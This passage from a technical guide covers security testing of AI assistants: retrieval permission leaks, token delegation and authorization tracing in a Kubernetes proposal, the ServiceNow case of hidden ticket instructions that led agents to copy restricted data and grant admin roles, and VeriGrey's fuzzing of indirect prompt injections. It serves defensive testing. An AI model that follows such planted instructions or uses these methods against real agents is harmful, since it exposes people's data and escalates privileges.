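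*Audience-Bound Persistent Memory* (2026), a study of assistants that store information between conversations, found no such loss. Filtering after search returned the permitted items just as often as checking authorization before ranking, but only eight distracting items competed for 20 places. Results from such a small test collection may therefore be misleading. In the same study, unrestricted retrieval put forbidden items into 82% of 100,000 prompts, while checking authorization before ranking put them into none of 200,000.

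Liu and colleagues cite a 2026 study by Rohith Namboothiri in which filtering after search exposed forbidden context in 86.1% of queries, whereas Arceo and Narsing's filter let no forbidden documents through. The results are compatible if Namboothiri counted documents when the search fetched them and Arceo and Narsing counted them after filtering.

Many databases can apply permission rules themselves, row by row. Liu and colleagues cite a test in which this cut leakage between tenants from 0.2% to zero over 1,000 queries, and they conclude that checking permissions early is much safer. However, Espiritu and Cash (2026) showed in *Plaintext Recovery Against Post-Filtering Access Control* that PostgreSQL, a widely used database, can run parts of some queries over all the rows before it applies the permission rule. The response time then depends on rows the user can't see, and they used this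 to reconstruct entire hidden records. They also recovered words from hidden documents in two text-search systems, whose ranking scores depended on those documents. Their case studies don't cover vector search, which finds passages by comparing their embeddings, and someone who can only put questions to an assistant has much less control over the database query. But a tester wouldn't find this kind of leak in a retrieval trace, because every list of results would contain only documents the user is allowed to see.

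A company could instead build a separate index for each role, so that no search touches a forbidden document, but it must then store shared documents several times. In *Don't Stir the Pot! Authorized Vector Data Retrieval via Access-Aware Indexing*, Han, Chakraborty and Mehrotra (2026) give a small example with three roles in which separate indexes hold 1.5 times as many entries as one shared index. Their design, VEDA, copies some groups of documents and merges others within a storage limit. When each query came from a single role, VEDA was 2.24 to 5.60 times faster than an earlier system, SIEVE, and 8.69 to 42.61 times faster than another, HoneyBee. A merged index still contains documents that some of its users are not allowed to read. The search discards them as it runs, but a span created inside the search may still list them.

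### Stale permissions, shared caches and missing tenant filters

Many applications copy each document's access label into the search index when they index it, because checking the source system during every search would be slow. If a manager later removes the accounts department from a folder, the label on every chunk from that folder is wrong until someone updates the index. The trace will show that the filter ran and the document passed it. Arceo and Narsing's guarantee of zero leakage assumes that ownership labels never change after a document enters the index. That may be reasonable for a customer's own files, but not for personnel files, where access changes whenever somebody moves jobs.

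Deleted documents can also remain in an index. Liu and colleagues describe research showing that entries marked as deleted stay in a common type of vector index, and that attackers can turn them back into text until someone rebuilds the index. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) notes more generally that anyone who can read the vector store can read the documents, so the store needs its own access controls.

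An application may also cache an answer and reuse it when someone asks the same question. If it matches cached answers by question alone, Ana could receive one written for the head of personnel. Her trace would contain no document search, so a tester who looked only at retrieval spans would find nothing wrong. *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025) notes that some frameworks offer tenant tags to keep caches separate. Arceo and Narsing warn that retrieved text can also stay in a conversation without a new permission check at each turn, so someone who loses access to a file at noon could still get answers about it in a conversation that began that morning.

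A missing tenant filter can be a simple programming mistake. A developer might filter the main search but forget to filter a "find similar documents" button added later. Vector search makes this worse because it normally returns the closest passages even if none is a good match, so another tenant's text can fill the remaining results. An attacker may also word a question to fall close to another tenant's documents, as *Systematization of Knowledge* describes. A tester can look for missing filters by grouping search spans by the feature that produced them and checking that each group has a filter.

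### A test with two identities

This invented test uses two accounts, one for Ana and one for Ruth, who runs the personnel department. The tester writes three documents about made-up people: a health file, a pay review and a plan to close an office. Each contains a code word that appears nowhere else. Ruth may open all three, and Ana should not be able to open any. To check for stale permissions, the tester gives the accounts department access to the pay review, waits for the index to copy that permission, and then withdraws that access.

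On Tuesday the tester asks 40 questions from Ruth's account and then the same 40 from Ana's. Some are ordinary questions about leave and pay, and others resemble the seeded documents. Ruth's run is the control. If her searches never return the seeded documents, the questions are too weak or the documents aren't in the index, and a clean result for Ana would not show that her access is restricted. Ruth goes first so that any shared cache already holds her results and could leak them to Ana.

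Each of Ana's 40 traces contains a search that returned five chunks, for a total of 200. The tester first searches the answers for the code words and finds one disclosure, from the health file. The tester then reads the answers and finds another, in which the assistant paraphrased the pay review and left out the code word. An endpoint-level tester would stop here and report 2 failures in 40.

The tester then exports a row for each of the 200 chunks, with the trace identifier, the user, the time of the search and the document identifier. For each row, the tester asks the source system, where the company keeps the original documents, whether Ana could open that document at that time. This is the result for the three seeded documents and for an ordinary supplier contract:

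| Document | Ana's questions that retrieved it | Index label allows Ana | Source allowed Ana on Tuesday | Source allows Ana on Thursday |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Health file | 4 | No | No | No |
| Pay review | 3 | Yes | No | No |
| Office closure plan | 2 | No | No | Yes |
| Supplier contract | 1 | Yes | Yes | No |

No question retrieved more than one of these documents, and Ana could open everything else her searches returned. The join therefore finds all 9 questions that retrieved a forbidden chunk, including the 7 with harmless answers.

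The time of the lookup matters because managers changed two permissions on Wednesday. They gave the accounts department access to the closure plan and removed its access to the supplier contract. A tester who compared Tuesday's traces with Thursday's permissions would miss the two questions about the closure plan and wrongly report the one about the contract. If the source system doesn't keep a history of permissions, the tester should export them immediately before and after the run.

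Counting by the index's own labels would be even less accurate, because it would miss all three questions about the pay review. But the labels do help to find the cause. The search returned the health file and the closure plan even though their labels were correct, so it can't have applied a filter. The pay review would have passed a working filter because its label was out of date. If the developers only add the missing filter, 3 of the 9 questions will still fail.

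The tester also reads the input messages, in case a later check removed the forbidden chunks. In 6 of the 9 requests, the forbidden text was in the prompt. In the other 3, the application included only the three top-ranked chunks, and the forbidden one ranked fourth or fifth.

The tester wrote many of the questions to reach forbidden files, so nine out of 40 is not an estimate of how often staff questions reach them. For a product with exclusion rules like Copilot's, the lookup should also check whether the assistant may process the document. Without that check, the join would have passed all the confidential emails.

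### Is retrieval without disclosure a vulnerability?

The developers of Ana's assistant might object that 7 of the 9 answers disclosed nothing restricted. Software routinely reads data that its users can't. A mail server, for example, processes everyone's email, and an application that filters after search has to fetch some forbidden documents to reject them. If testers reported every such read as a breach, the serious faults would be hard to find among the reports. Microsoft defended Copilot similarly, saying its access controls had remained intact, although it accepted that the product had not behaved as intended.

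Others, such as Phil Windley in *Authorization Before Retrieval* (2026), hold that the model should never receive data the user may not see. Arceo and Narsing assume that a model may leak anything in its prompt, so the application has to settle permissions before it builds the prompt. Even if one answer leaves out the restricted text, repeating or rewording the question might reveal it. The text has also gone to the company that runs the model, and possibly into a trace store that people without access to health files can read. *How to Secure RAG Workflows*, from the identity software company Okta, places retrieval with excessive permissions under "Sensitive Information Disclosure" in the list of LLM risks from OWASP, a software security organisation.

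The best way to judge a particular case is to find out what stopped the chunk. If code checked Ana's permissions and removed the health file before the model call, the retrieval was a normal step in a working control. Espiritu and Cash's attacks are a reason to prefer an earlier filter, but they don't show that this application leaks. If the file entered the prompt and only the model's choice of words kept it from Ana, the application has a vulnerability, even if the answers were harmless. The 3 chunks that ranked too low to enter the prompt also show a vulnerability, because the application removed them for their rank rather than Ana's permissions, and a slightly different question could have ranked them higher. All 9 questions therefore belong in the tester's report, with the 2 disclosures marked as the most serious.

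## Whose authority an agent used: the Kubernetes proposal for recording access decisions

The tester could check Ana's document searches by comparing the results with her permissions. Her leave lookup is harder to check. It went through the shared account hr-assistant, so Ana's own permissions may not have affected the answer.

Proposal 0033 of the Kubernetes agentic networking project would give testers a standard record of access checks. Kubernetes is open-source software for running applications across many machines, and the project works on how AI agents connect to tools and to each other. The project has not settled the proposal's details. The proposal's spans, or trace records, will also be of little use to testers who don't know which of several identities was checked.

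### The identities behind one tool call

An MCP deployment may involve a user, a host application, several clients and servers, authorization servers, and the databases or other systems behind them (Tabata, *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, 2026). An authorization server issues access tokens, which programs present to each other to show what they are allowed to do. These are unrelated to the tokens of text that models read.

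Ana's leave lookup involves four identities. Ana asked the question, and an agent called staff-assistant chose the tool. An MCP server called leave-server ran the lookup, using the account hr-assistant to reach the personnel system. The first trace of her request recorded only Ana and the account.

A confused deputy is a privileged program that someone induces to misuse its authority. Suppose Ana asks for Tomas's leave balance and leave-server fetches it through hr-assistant. The personnel system correctly allows this, because hr-assistant may read everyone's leave. Ana gets the balance without stealing a password, because leave-server has more authority than she does and uses it for her. One remedy is to send the user's identity with the request, so that the last system to receive it can apply that user's limits.

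### Tokens that name the user and the agent

OAuth is a widely used standard for giving programs limited access to web services. *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (RFC 8693), by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, extends it so that a program can give an authorization server one token and get back another that suits the next system. The request must include a subject token, which represents the person or program on whose behalf the caller is asking. It may also include an actor token, which represents whoever will act.

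This invented token could result from an exchange in which Ana is the subject and the agent is the actor:

```
{
  "iss":   "https://login.company.example",
  "aud":   "https://leave-server.company.example",
  "exp":   1791360300,
  "scope": "leave.read",
  "sub":   "ana",
  "act":   { "sub": "staff-assistant" }
}
```

Each line is a claim. The first three give the server that issued the token, the server that should accept it and the time it expires. The scope limits the holder to reading leave records. The subject, `sub`, is Ana, and the actor claim, `act`, shows that staff-assistant is acting for her. Authorization servers typically sign tokens, so leave-server can detect if someone has changed a name.

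If the request has no actor token, the result can only be impersonation. The new token has Ana as its subject and no actor, so the receiving system can't distinguish the agent from Ana. A tester who finds `sub: ana` without an actor claim therefore can't tell whether Ana or an agent opened the record.

When leave-server needs to call the personnel system, it can exchange the token again. The subject is still Ana, leave-server becomes the current actor, and staff-assistant moves into a second actor claim nested inside the first. This gives the tester a history of the request. However, RFC 8693 allows the personnel system to base its decision only on the current actor and the token's top-level claims, such as the subject. A company therefore can't keep staff-assistant away from medical leave by having the personnel system check the nested claim.

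The standard also allows Ana's original token to contain a `may_act` claim listing who may act for her, so a tester can attempt an exchange as an agent not on the list and see whether the authorization server refuses. The exchange doesn't closely link the new token to the old one, so if an administrator withdraws Ana's access halfway through a task, the agent's token may keep working until it expires. A tester can check for this too.

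OAuth tokens often also contain a client identifier, which is easy to mistake for the agent's identity. In *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation*, McGuinness (2026) separates the client identifier, which refers to an application's registration, from the subject who gave the authority and the actor using it. The document is one person's draft, not an adopted standard. McGuinness argues that existing standards have no consistent way to represent these relationships across different kinds of token, so a tester should ask what each field means in the product under test.

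### MCP's rule against passing tokens on

Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) forbids an MCP server to pass a token it receives to the systems behind it. This rules out the simplest design, in which leave-server would forward its token to the personnel system. A server must check that the token it receives was meant for it, and must get a separate token for the systems behind it from their own authorization server. The document also warns of a confused deputy problem when an MCP server stands between many clients and an outside service and uses one fixed client identity for all of them. An attacker with a stolen authorization code could then obtain access without the user's consent, so such a server must ask the user to approve each newly registered client.

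MCP doesn't specify whose name the separate token should carry, and Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) doesn't list RFC 8693 among its standards. Leave-server could exchange Ana's token for one that still names her, or it could log in as hr-assistant and drop her name. Both designs follow the rule, so a tester can't tell from a developer's assurance of MCP compliance whether Ana's limits apply in the personnel system. Authorization is also optional in MCP, and servers that run as local processes are supposed to get their credentials from their environment instead.

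An agent's permissions can also grow during a task. When a server refuses a call because the token's scope is too narrow, a client acting for a user should request a new token that covers both its earlier scopes and the missing one. A tester should therefore check the trace for the token's scope at each call, not only at login. The trace should record the token's relevant claims but not the token itself, because attackers can use tokens they find in a server's logs, according to the Model Context Protocol.

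### What proposal 0033 would record

The Kubernetes Agentic Networking proposal, *Observability in Agentic Networking*, covers gateways and similar proxies that sit between agents and MCP servers. For each tool call, the gateway would create an `mcp.authorization` span for the whole authorization check and, beneath it, an `mcp.authorization.rule` span for each rule it evaluated. Guardrail checks would have similar spans.

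The proposal adds two attributes. `event.action` is "allow" or "deny". `event.outcome` records whether the check itself worked, so when the gateway completes the check and refuses access, the action is "deny" and the outcome is "success". If the gateway couldn't complete the check, the outcome should be "failure" or "unknown", and a tester would want to know whether the action was still "allow".

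Many gateways refuse any call that no rule allows. These refusals can be confusing in an ordinary log, because no rule seems to have caused them. Under the proposal, the gateway would create an extra rule span called `default-deny`, so the tester could see that the gateway had checked the call and found no rule that allowed it.

The proposal illustrates this with a customer support agent that tries to delete a customer's data. The tree below is a shortened version of that example:

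```
gen_ai.tool.call             delete_customer_data     status: OK
|
+-- mcp.gateway.request      HTTP status: 403         status: ERROR
    |
    +-- mcp.authorization    action: deny             outcome: success
    |   |
    |   +-- rule: read_only_support   match: false    action: allow
    |   +-- rule: admin_only_delete   match: false    action: allow
    |   +-- rule: default-deny        match: true     action: allow
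    |
    +-- mcp.audit.log        authorization_failure    outcome: failure
```

The gateway refused the deletion, but a careless search of these spans could suggest that it was allowed. The agent's own span has the status "OK", so a tester needs the gateway's spans to see the refusal. The first two rules have the action "allow", which is what they would have done if they had matched, but neither did. In the authorization span, "outcome" shows that the check worked, while in the audit span it shows that the request failed.

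The `default-deny` span in the example mistakenly has the action "allow", where the proposal's text requires "deny". If someone built a gateway from the example, a search for matching rules with the action "allow" would return refused calls. Testers should take the final decision from the parent span and report any case where it differs from the matching rule's action.

Evaluation stops at the rule that decides the request, so a trace can't show whether a later rule would have led to a different decision. Retries would share a trace identifier even when the agent changes the arguments or switches to another tool. That would help a tester find cases where an agent was refused a deletion and then looked for another way to carry it out.

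The weakest part of the proposal is how it handles the user's identity. It sends `user.id` and `agent.id` in W3C Baggage, a web header that carries named values along with the request. The project chose baggage because gateways may need these identifiers for authorization and other decisions. But the proposal describes no way to check them, and any program that can write the header can set them to any value. The authorization spans in the example have no user attribute. Only an error message refers to the person, and it gives just the role "support_agent", so the example wouldn't show which employee had asked for the deletion.

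### What exists today

Kubernetes Agentic Networking's *All Proposals by Status* lists proposal 0033 as provisional, which the project defines as meaning that the goals are agreed but the implementation is not yet. An assessor should check whether its status has changed. The proposal does not cover how operators would turn these records on. A separate draft, Kubernetes Gateway API's *Standardized Telemetry API*, covers settings of that kind.

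The project has a prototype that enforces access rules, but its documentation doesn't describe an implementation of the tracing spans. Kubernetes Agentic Networking's *Tool Authorization in Agentic Networking* explains that an agent may list a server's tools by default but may call one only if a rule allows it. A rule can let one agent use "add" and "subtract" on a calculator server and limit another to "subtract". The design is provisional and, according to the document, should not be used in production.

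These rules apply to the agent's identity, not the user's. They identify an agent by its Kubernetes service account or its SPIFFE identity, a standardized name for a running program. *Dynamic Auth*, a Kubernetes Agentic Networking proposal to extend the rules, would also accept identity tokens from a company's login system, but the prototype doesn't support them yet. If Ana and Ruth both use staff-assistant, the prototype treats their requests as coming from the same caller. The prototype can also send the decision to an outside authorization service, which could take the user into account if it could reliably identify them.

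### Three traces of Ana's leave lookup

These traces are invented, and their field names are simplified. In each one, Ana asks for her own leave balance and gets the right answer. The gateway creates the authorization span, and the personnel system creates the other span.

```
CORRECT DELEGATION
  authorization      user: ana               agent: staff-assistant
                     resource: leave/ana     decision: allow
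  personnel system   subject: ana            actor: leave-server
                     resource: leave/ana

SHARED SERVICE ACCOUNT
  authorization      user: none              agent: staff-assistant
                     resource: leave/ana     decision: allow
  personnel system   subject: hr-assistant   actor: none
                     resource: leave/ana

DECISION FOR ANA, ACCESS AS HR-ASSISTANT
  authorization      user: ana               agent: staff-assistant
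                     resource: leave/ana     decision: allow
  personnel system   subject: hr-assistant   actor: none
                     resource: leave/ana
```

With correct delegation, Ana is the user in the gateway's decision and the subject when the personnel system opens the record. With the shared account, her name appears in neither place. In the last trace, the gateway approved the request for Ana, but leave-server then used hr-assistant to fetch the record. That trace's authorization span is identical to the one for correct delegation, so a tester who reads only that span would miss the difference, which appears in the subject recorded by the personnel system.

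The last design can be safe if leave-server fetches exactly what the gateway approved. But if a bug made leave-server ignore the employee number, it could fetch everyone's leave, and the personnel system wouldn't block the request. The tester should therefore compare the resource in the two spans as well as the identity.

A request from Ana's account for Tomas's leave balance is a better test. With correct delegation, the personnel system can refuse the request because the token's subject is Ana, even if the gateway mistakenly allows it. With the shared account, none of the steps in the trace would stop her. In the last design, the result depends on whether the gateway's rule checks the employee number. The Kubernetes prototype's simplest rules match only the tool's name, so a rule that allowed the leave lookup would allow it for any employee.

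All of this assumes that the names in the trace are true. Some come from a credential that another component checked, and others are text from the application. According to its *Span attribute reference*, agentgateway, an existing gateway, records a token's subject (`jwt.sub`) if it used the token to authenticate the request, and a program's identity (`src.identity`) if the program connected with a certificate. The default attributes don't include the actor claim, though developers can add other attributes.

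| Identity in the record | Where the value comes from | What it supports |
|---|---|---|
| `user.id` in baggage | The application | The application claimed to be acting for this user |
| `gen_ai.agent.id` | The application's instrumentation | The application used this name for the agent |
| `jwt.sub` | A token that the gateway checked | An authorization server issued a token for this subject |
| Actor claim, if recorded after a check | The same token | An authorization server named this program as the actor |
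| `src.identity` | The caller's certificate | This program connected, for an unknown user |
| Account in the personnel system's log | The personnel system's own login check | The data was opened under this account |

The first two are unverified claims. A tester can check whether an application relies on them by sending a request with Ana's token and Ruth's name in the baggage header. If the answer includes something only Ruth may see, some component relied on the header instead of the token. Even a value from a checked token reaches the trace as a copy, so the tester also has to trust the gateway that copied it.

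### ServiceNow: the right user and the wrong instructions

An agent can act under the correct user's authority and still be a confused deputy. ServiceNow sells software for managing support tickets and other internal company work, and its Now Assist agents can read and change the records in it. *ServiceNow AI Agents Can Be Tricked* (The Hacker News, November 2025) reported that AppOmni, a security company, had shown how a user with few permissions could exploit these agents.

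Aaron Costello, a researcher at AppOmni, set up an account that could create tickets but couldn't read other people's. He used it to write a ticket containing hidden instructions for any agent that read it. When an administrator later asked an agent to work on that ticket, the agent got help from a more powerful one, which read a ticket that Costello's account couldn't read and copied its contents into the ticket he had written. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to give a malicious user the administrator role.

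According to AppOmni, Now Assist agents run with the privileges of the user who started the interaction, unless someone configures them otherwise. AppOmni also says that ServiceNow's security staff confirmed the behaviour was intended and updated the documentation. The finding comes from a demonstration, not a known attack on a customer, and AppOmni has an interest in it because it sells a product that monitors these agents. But ServiceNow's reported response suggests that the two companies largely agreed about how the agents work.

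If a gateway had recorded this attack with the fields from the three traces, every entry could have been correct. The user was the administrator, the agent was acting for the administrator, and the administrator was allowed to read the closed ticket. No shared service account was involved. But the instructions came from someone else, and none of the identity fields records who wrote the text an agent follows.

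To find the cause, a tester would need the input messages, to see that the instructions arrived in a ticket, and the ticket system's records, to see who wrote it. AppOmni recommends comparing the original task with the tools that the agents used. An agent that is supposed to categorise one ticket has little reason to read another and copy its text. The attack worked only where tools could run without a person's approval, so AppOmni advises companies to require approval for tools that change records or send email. It also advises them to put agents with different duties in separate teams.

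Sometimes the recorded user is wrong from the start. CX Today's *AppOmni Uncovers Agentic AI Security Vulnerability in ServiceNow's API and Agents* describes a separate finding in which an attacker could impersonate an administrator and run an agent under that account. The trace might then name the administrator at every step, even though the administrator had made no request.

### Why a recorded "allow" can be wrong

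An authorization span records what the software decided under its policy, which may be wrong. Dynamic Auth warns against rules that allow anyone whose role isn't "blocked", because they give access to every role that whoever wrote them didn't think of. If Ana had no role, such a rule could let her in, and the trace would record a successful check.

The software can also compare the wrong fields. In MCP, a request to read a resource, such as a file, identifies it by address. According to Kubernetes Agentic Networking's *Introduction*, the prototype looks for a name instead, a known limitation that the project plans to fix. A rule meant to allow one file may therefore never match. If a request contained an approved name and another file's address, the gateway might allow it because of the name.

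The same rule can mean different things in two products. Dynamic Auth points out that `request.path` includes the query string (the part of a web address after the question mark) in the Envoy proxy but not in agentgateway. A company that moves its rules unchanged from one to the other could get different decisions.

A tester should therefore compare recorded decisions with an independent list of who is supposed to have access, as in the test of Ana's document searches. The tester also needs the policy as it stood when the decision was made. Proposal 0033's example gives the policy's name but no version, so a later reader couldn't tell which version produced the decision.

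### Why a missing decision does not mean a missing check

An authorization check may have run without leaving a span. The agentgateway reference describes separate spans for calls to outside policy services, such as an authorization service, but not for each rule the gateway evaluates itself. If a filter drops the main request span, all the policy spans beneath it disappear too. A policy span's fixed attributes include the service's response status but no field for "allow" or "deny".

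The personnel system's own log may also record an access decision, so the tester should look there before reporting that no system checked Ana's permissions. If a request from Ana's account for Tomas's balance succeeds, the tester has found a fault whether or not a check ran.

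## VeriGrey: using recorded tool calls to guide security tests

In the tests described so far, the tester sent a request and then read the trace to see what had happened. A trace can also help the tester choose the next request. VeriGrey, a research tool published by the National University of Singapore in March 2026, records which tools an agent calls and uses the record to decide which test inputs to develop further. In its developers' experiments, VeriGrey got agents to carry out harmful tasks much more often than a testing tool that did not use records of tool calls, but most of the gain came from how VeriGrey writes its inputs.

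### Fuzzing, and why code coverage says little about an agent

Fuzzing automatically generates large numbers of test inputs to find some that make a program misbehave. A coverage-guided fuzzer also records which parts of the program's code each input runs. *NeuronFuzz* (2026) lists the typical components of such a fuzzer as a collection of starting inputs called seeds, a scheduler that chooses among them, a mutator that changes them, instrumentation, and feedback from each run. The fuzzer gives more "energy", meaning more trials, to inputs that reach new code.

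Suppose a program that opens images crashes only when a compressed image has a damaged size field. Random changes to a file would rarely produce both conditions at once. A coverage-guided fuzzer detects when a change first makes the program run its decompression code, saves that file, and keeps changing it until the size field is damaged.

This works because an ordinary program's decisions are written in its code. In an agent, the model makes most of the decisions, and the code around it repeats a short loop of model calls and tool calls. Almost the same lines run whether Ana's assistant emails her manager or a stranger, so tests that covered all the code could still miss the harmful case.

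A fuzzer could ignore the code and check only whether each attack succeeded. Wang, Siu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentVigil*, built a black-box fuzzer of this kind and warned that such sparse feedback can reduce the search to random guessing. They partly compensated by favoring inputs that succeeded on tasks where earlier ones had failed. But this feedback still doesn't distinguish between failures. Tool calls can distinguish a run in which the agent ignored the planted text from one in which it started the harmful task and got stuck.

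### How VeriGrey chooses its next test

VeriGrey tests agents for indirect prompt injection. Each campaign has one ordinary user task, several harmful goals, and a seed for each goal. A seed is text that an attacker could plant in something the agent reads. VeriGrey picks a seed, has a language model rewrite it, runs the agent, and checks whether the agent carried out the goal. It continues until the agent has carried out every goal or the campaign runs out of trials.

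A developer records the calls by adding a small wrapper to each tool. The wrapper records the tool's name and arguments, then runs the tool. If an application's tool spans already include the arguments, they could supply this feedback without new instrumentation. The search can't use calls from a tool that has neither a wrapper nor a span.

After each run, VeriGrey compares the agent's tool calls with those from earlier runs. It checks for a tool the agent had not called before, a new transition (one tool called directly after another for the first time), and a new overall sequence. If the sequence is new, VeriGrey keeps the input. It then creates one additional variant of that input for each of the three criteria the run met. The model that writes the variants also receives the previous input and the tool calls it produced, so it can try to identify why the attempt failed.

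In this invented example, the assistant can search documents, look up leave records and send email. The harmful goal is to email a leave record outside the company. For brevity, the example compares only the tools' names.

| Run | Tool calls, in order | New tool | New transition | New sequence | Variants earned |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | search, leave lookup | Yes | Yes | Yes | 3 |
| 2 | search, leave lookup | No | No | No | 0 |
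| 3 | leave lookup, search | No | Yes | Yes | 2 |
| 4 | search, leave lookup, search | No | No | Yes | 1 |
| 5 | search, leave lookup, email | Yes | Yes | Yes | 3 |

Run 1 meets all three criteria only because there were no earlier runs to compare it with. Run 4 contains two transitions that had each occurred before, but never in the same run. In run 5 the assistant emails the leave record to Ana herself, so the attack fails, as it does in the other four runs. A fuzzer that recorded only success or failure would treat all five inputs alike. VeriGrey gives the fifth input three more variants, which is sensible because that input got the assistant to put a leave record in an email.

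A new sequence of tool calls isn't necessarily dangerous. VeriGrey also creates a variant of an input that only makes the agent search three times instead of twice. Some harmful runs have ordinary sequences. If the assistant looked up Tomas's leave instead of Ana's, the tool names would be the same as in a harmless run. VeriGrey can detect this change because it labels each call with both its name and its arguments, but a slightly reworded search query could then make a routine run look new. The arguments would not help if a search for Ana returned Tomas's medical file, because the wrapper doesn't record results. The order of the calls also doesn't prove that data from one tool reached the next, which is the problem ChainFuzzer addresses.

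### Results on AgentDojo

VeriGrey's developers compared it with a black-box fuzzer on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated environments for office work, Slack messaging, travel booking and banking. After each run, code checks the state of the environment, for example to see whether the agent sent an email, so an attack doesn't count as successful just because the agent claims to have carried it out (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, *AgentDojo*, 2024).

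The developers ran one campaign for every combination of the benchmark's 97 user tasks, two fuzzers and three models, 582 in total. Campaigns had up to 100 runs each and an average of 8.7 harmful goals. The score is the share of those goals that the agent carried out at least once.

| Model | Black-box baseline | VeriGrey | Gain in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 37.7% | 70.7% | 33.0 |
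| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 36.8% | 47.4% | 10.6 |
| Qwen-3 235B | 67.6% | 81.7% | 14.1 |

These scores count a goal as reached if at least one of its roughly 11 runs in a campaign succeeded, so they don't measure the chance that a single attack works. The two measures can differ widely, as Hofer, Debenedetti and Tramèr (2026) found in *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments*. Their best method against GPT-5 succeeded in 4.7% of attempts, but over four separate searches it succeeded at least once for 30% of the pairs of user task and harmful goal.

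The scores also do not show which model is safest. In each campaign the same model ran the agent and wrote the attacks, so Qwen-3's high score could mean that it was easy to mislead or that it wrote effective attacks. The choice of attack writer can make a large difference. When Hofer and colleagues kept a small Qwen model as the target and replaced GPT-5-mini with GPT-5 as the writer of general-purpose attacks, the success rate rose from 10.7% to 45.2%. VeriGrey also had less room to improve on the baseline with Qwen-3, because the baseline had already reached every goal in the Slack environment.

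### How much of the gain came from the tool calls

VeriGrey differs from the baseline in its use of tool calls and also in how it writes its inputs. The baseline asks a model for a new version of the text without tying it to the user's task, while VeriGrey fits the text to what the user asked the agent to do. The developers switched off each feature in turn, using GPT-4.1 and all 97 tasks:

| | Ordinary inputs | Inputs fitted to the user's task |
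|---|---|---|
| Without tool-call feedback | 37.7% (baseline) | 59.6% |
| With tool-call feedback | 44.0% | 70.7% (VeriGrey) |

Without the feedback, VeriGrey's score fell by 11.1 points. The developers report a drop of 25.8 points without the fitted inputs, although the two scores they give, 70.7% and 44.0%, differ by 26.7. By either figure, removing the inputs lowered the score more than twice as much as removing the feedback, so the 33-point gain doesn't measure the value of traces.

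The two losses add up to more than 33 points because the features work better together. With ordinary inputs, feedback raised the score by only about 6 points, probably because tool calls reveal little when the agent recognises and ignores the planted text. Every such run looks like normal work. When the agent attempts the harmful task, its calls show how far it got. The comparison is approximate because the baseline's instructions for rewriting text differed from VeriGrey's. The developers also ran the comparison on only one model, so the value of feedback with the other two is unknown.

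Removing feedback lowered VeriGrey's score most on goals rated hard in AgentDojo, where it fell by 21.7 points, from 43.3% to 21.6%, compared with 9.0 points on easy goals and 9.9 on medium ones. VeriGrey's developers attribute this to hard goals usually taking more steps, because a search that rewards new sequences favours long ones. That is plausible, but the "hard" label is an imperfect guide to how many steps an attack needs, since the ratings also depend on how sensitive an action is, and VeriGrey scored higher on hard goals than on medium ones (30.1%).

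A stronger baseline might have narrowed the gap. AgentVigil's code was not public, so VeriGrey's developers wrote a simpler fuzzer inspired by it. Their version keeps every new input and changes each one once, whereas AgentVigil scores its inputs and uses a tree search to decide which to develop. Wang and colleagues reported a 71% success rate for AgentVigil on AgentDojo with the model o3-mini, but this isn't comparable with VeriGrey's 70.7% because the target model and set-up were different. Each version of VeriGrey was also tested in only one campaign per user task, so chance may account for some of the smaller differences. The section on replay discusses this problem.

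Recording a tool call requires no judgement, which is an advantage over another common source of feedback, a second model that judges each attempt. Hofer and colleagues used such a judge to choose which attacks to develop, and compared its verdicts with AgentDojo's own checks. When the judge predicted success, it was right 52.3% of the time for the small Qwen model and 29.4% of the time for GPT-5. A tester who uses tool calls still has to check separately whether the attack succeeded.

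### Defences that looked better under a weaker test

The developers also tested four defences, using GPT-4.1 and 31 user tasks chosen at random. The last column gives the share of user tasks that the agent completed when nobody attacked it.

| Defence | Black-box baseline | VeriGrey | User tasks completed, no attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 41.2% | 69.7% | 85.0% |
| Repeat the user's request after each tool call | 17.4% | 65.2% | 86.5% |
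| Mark tool results as data, not instructions | 36.4% | 67.6% | 81.0% |
| Stop the agent if a classifier detects an injection | 5.2% | 21.6% | 50.4% |
| Limit the agent to tools chosen before it starts | 12.8% | 17.4% | 81.7% |

Repeating the user's request more than halved successful attacks in the baseline tests but made hardly any difference against VeriGrey, so a company that tested only with the baseline would overestimate this defence. The classifier blocked many attacks, but it also stopped so much legitimate work that few companies would accept it.

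Limiting the tools gave the best balance. The model chooses the permitted tools from the user's request alone, before it reads anything an attacker could have planted, and software then blocks all other calls. Some attacks still succeeded because a tool that the task needs can also do harm. For example, an assistant needs its email tool to send Ana's leave form, so that tool remains available to an attacker.

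### Gemini CLI and OpenClaw

Gemini CLI is Google's coding agent for the command line. VeriGrey's developers tested it on a real bug fix, using ten harmful goals they wrote themselves, such as disclosing a secret file. VeriGrey achieved nine of the goals and the baseline achieved six. When the agent could use only tools chosen in advance, VeriGrey achieved five and the baseline three. The agent ran in a disposable environment with permission to take any action without asking, so the results don't show how often a person would have stopped it. Each group of five goals had only 50 runs because more would have cost too much.

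The developers also found that many of Gemini CLI's tools could work only inside the project's folder, but its command-line tool had no such limit. A trace containing only tool names is weak evidence for an agent like this, because listing a folder and copying a private key can both appear as one call to the command-line tool. A tester needs the arguments to tell them apart.

OpenClaw is a personal assistant that users extend with "skills", packages of code and written instructions that anyone can share. VeriGrey's developers started from 74 shared skills with signs of malicious intent and chose ten whose effects would be visible in the agent's record. In their original form, only one of the ten caused harm on each of three models. After VeriGrey rewrote them, with up to 20 runs for each skill, ten caused harm with Kimi-K2.5, nine with Claude Opus 4.6 and eight with GPT-5.2. This is good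 evidence that an agent that refuses a known malicious skill may not refuse a modified version. The test doesn't show whether tool-call feedback helped, because it compared the rewritten skills with the originals and didn't compare VeriGrey with another fuzzer.

### A simulated benchmark and older models

AgentDojo's agents work with invented emails and bank accounts in environments built for the benchmark. Zhou, Jiang and colleagues (2026), also from the National University of Singapore, caution in *GreyZone* that results from such benchmarks may not hold for deployed agents, where an attack has to get through the application's own interfaces and permission checks. GreyZone has 46 attack scenarios in ten independently developed applications, but it runs the applications locally and simulates some outside services.

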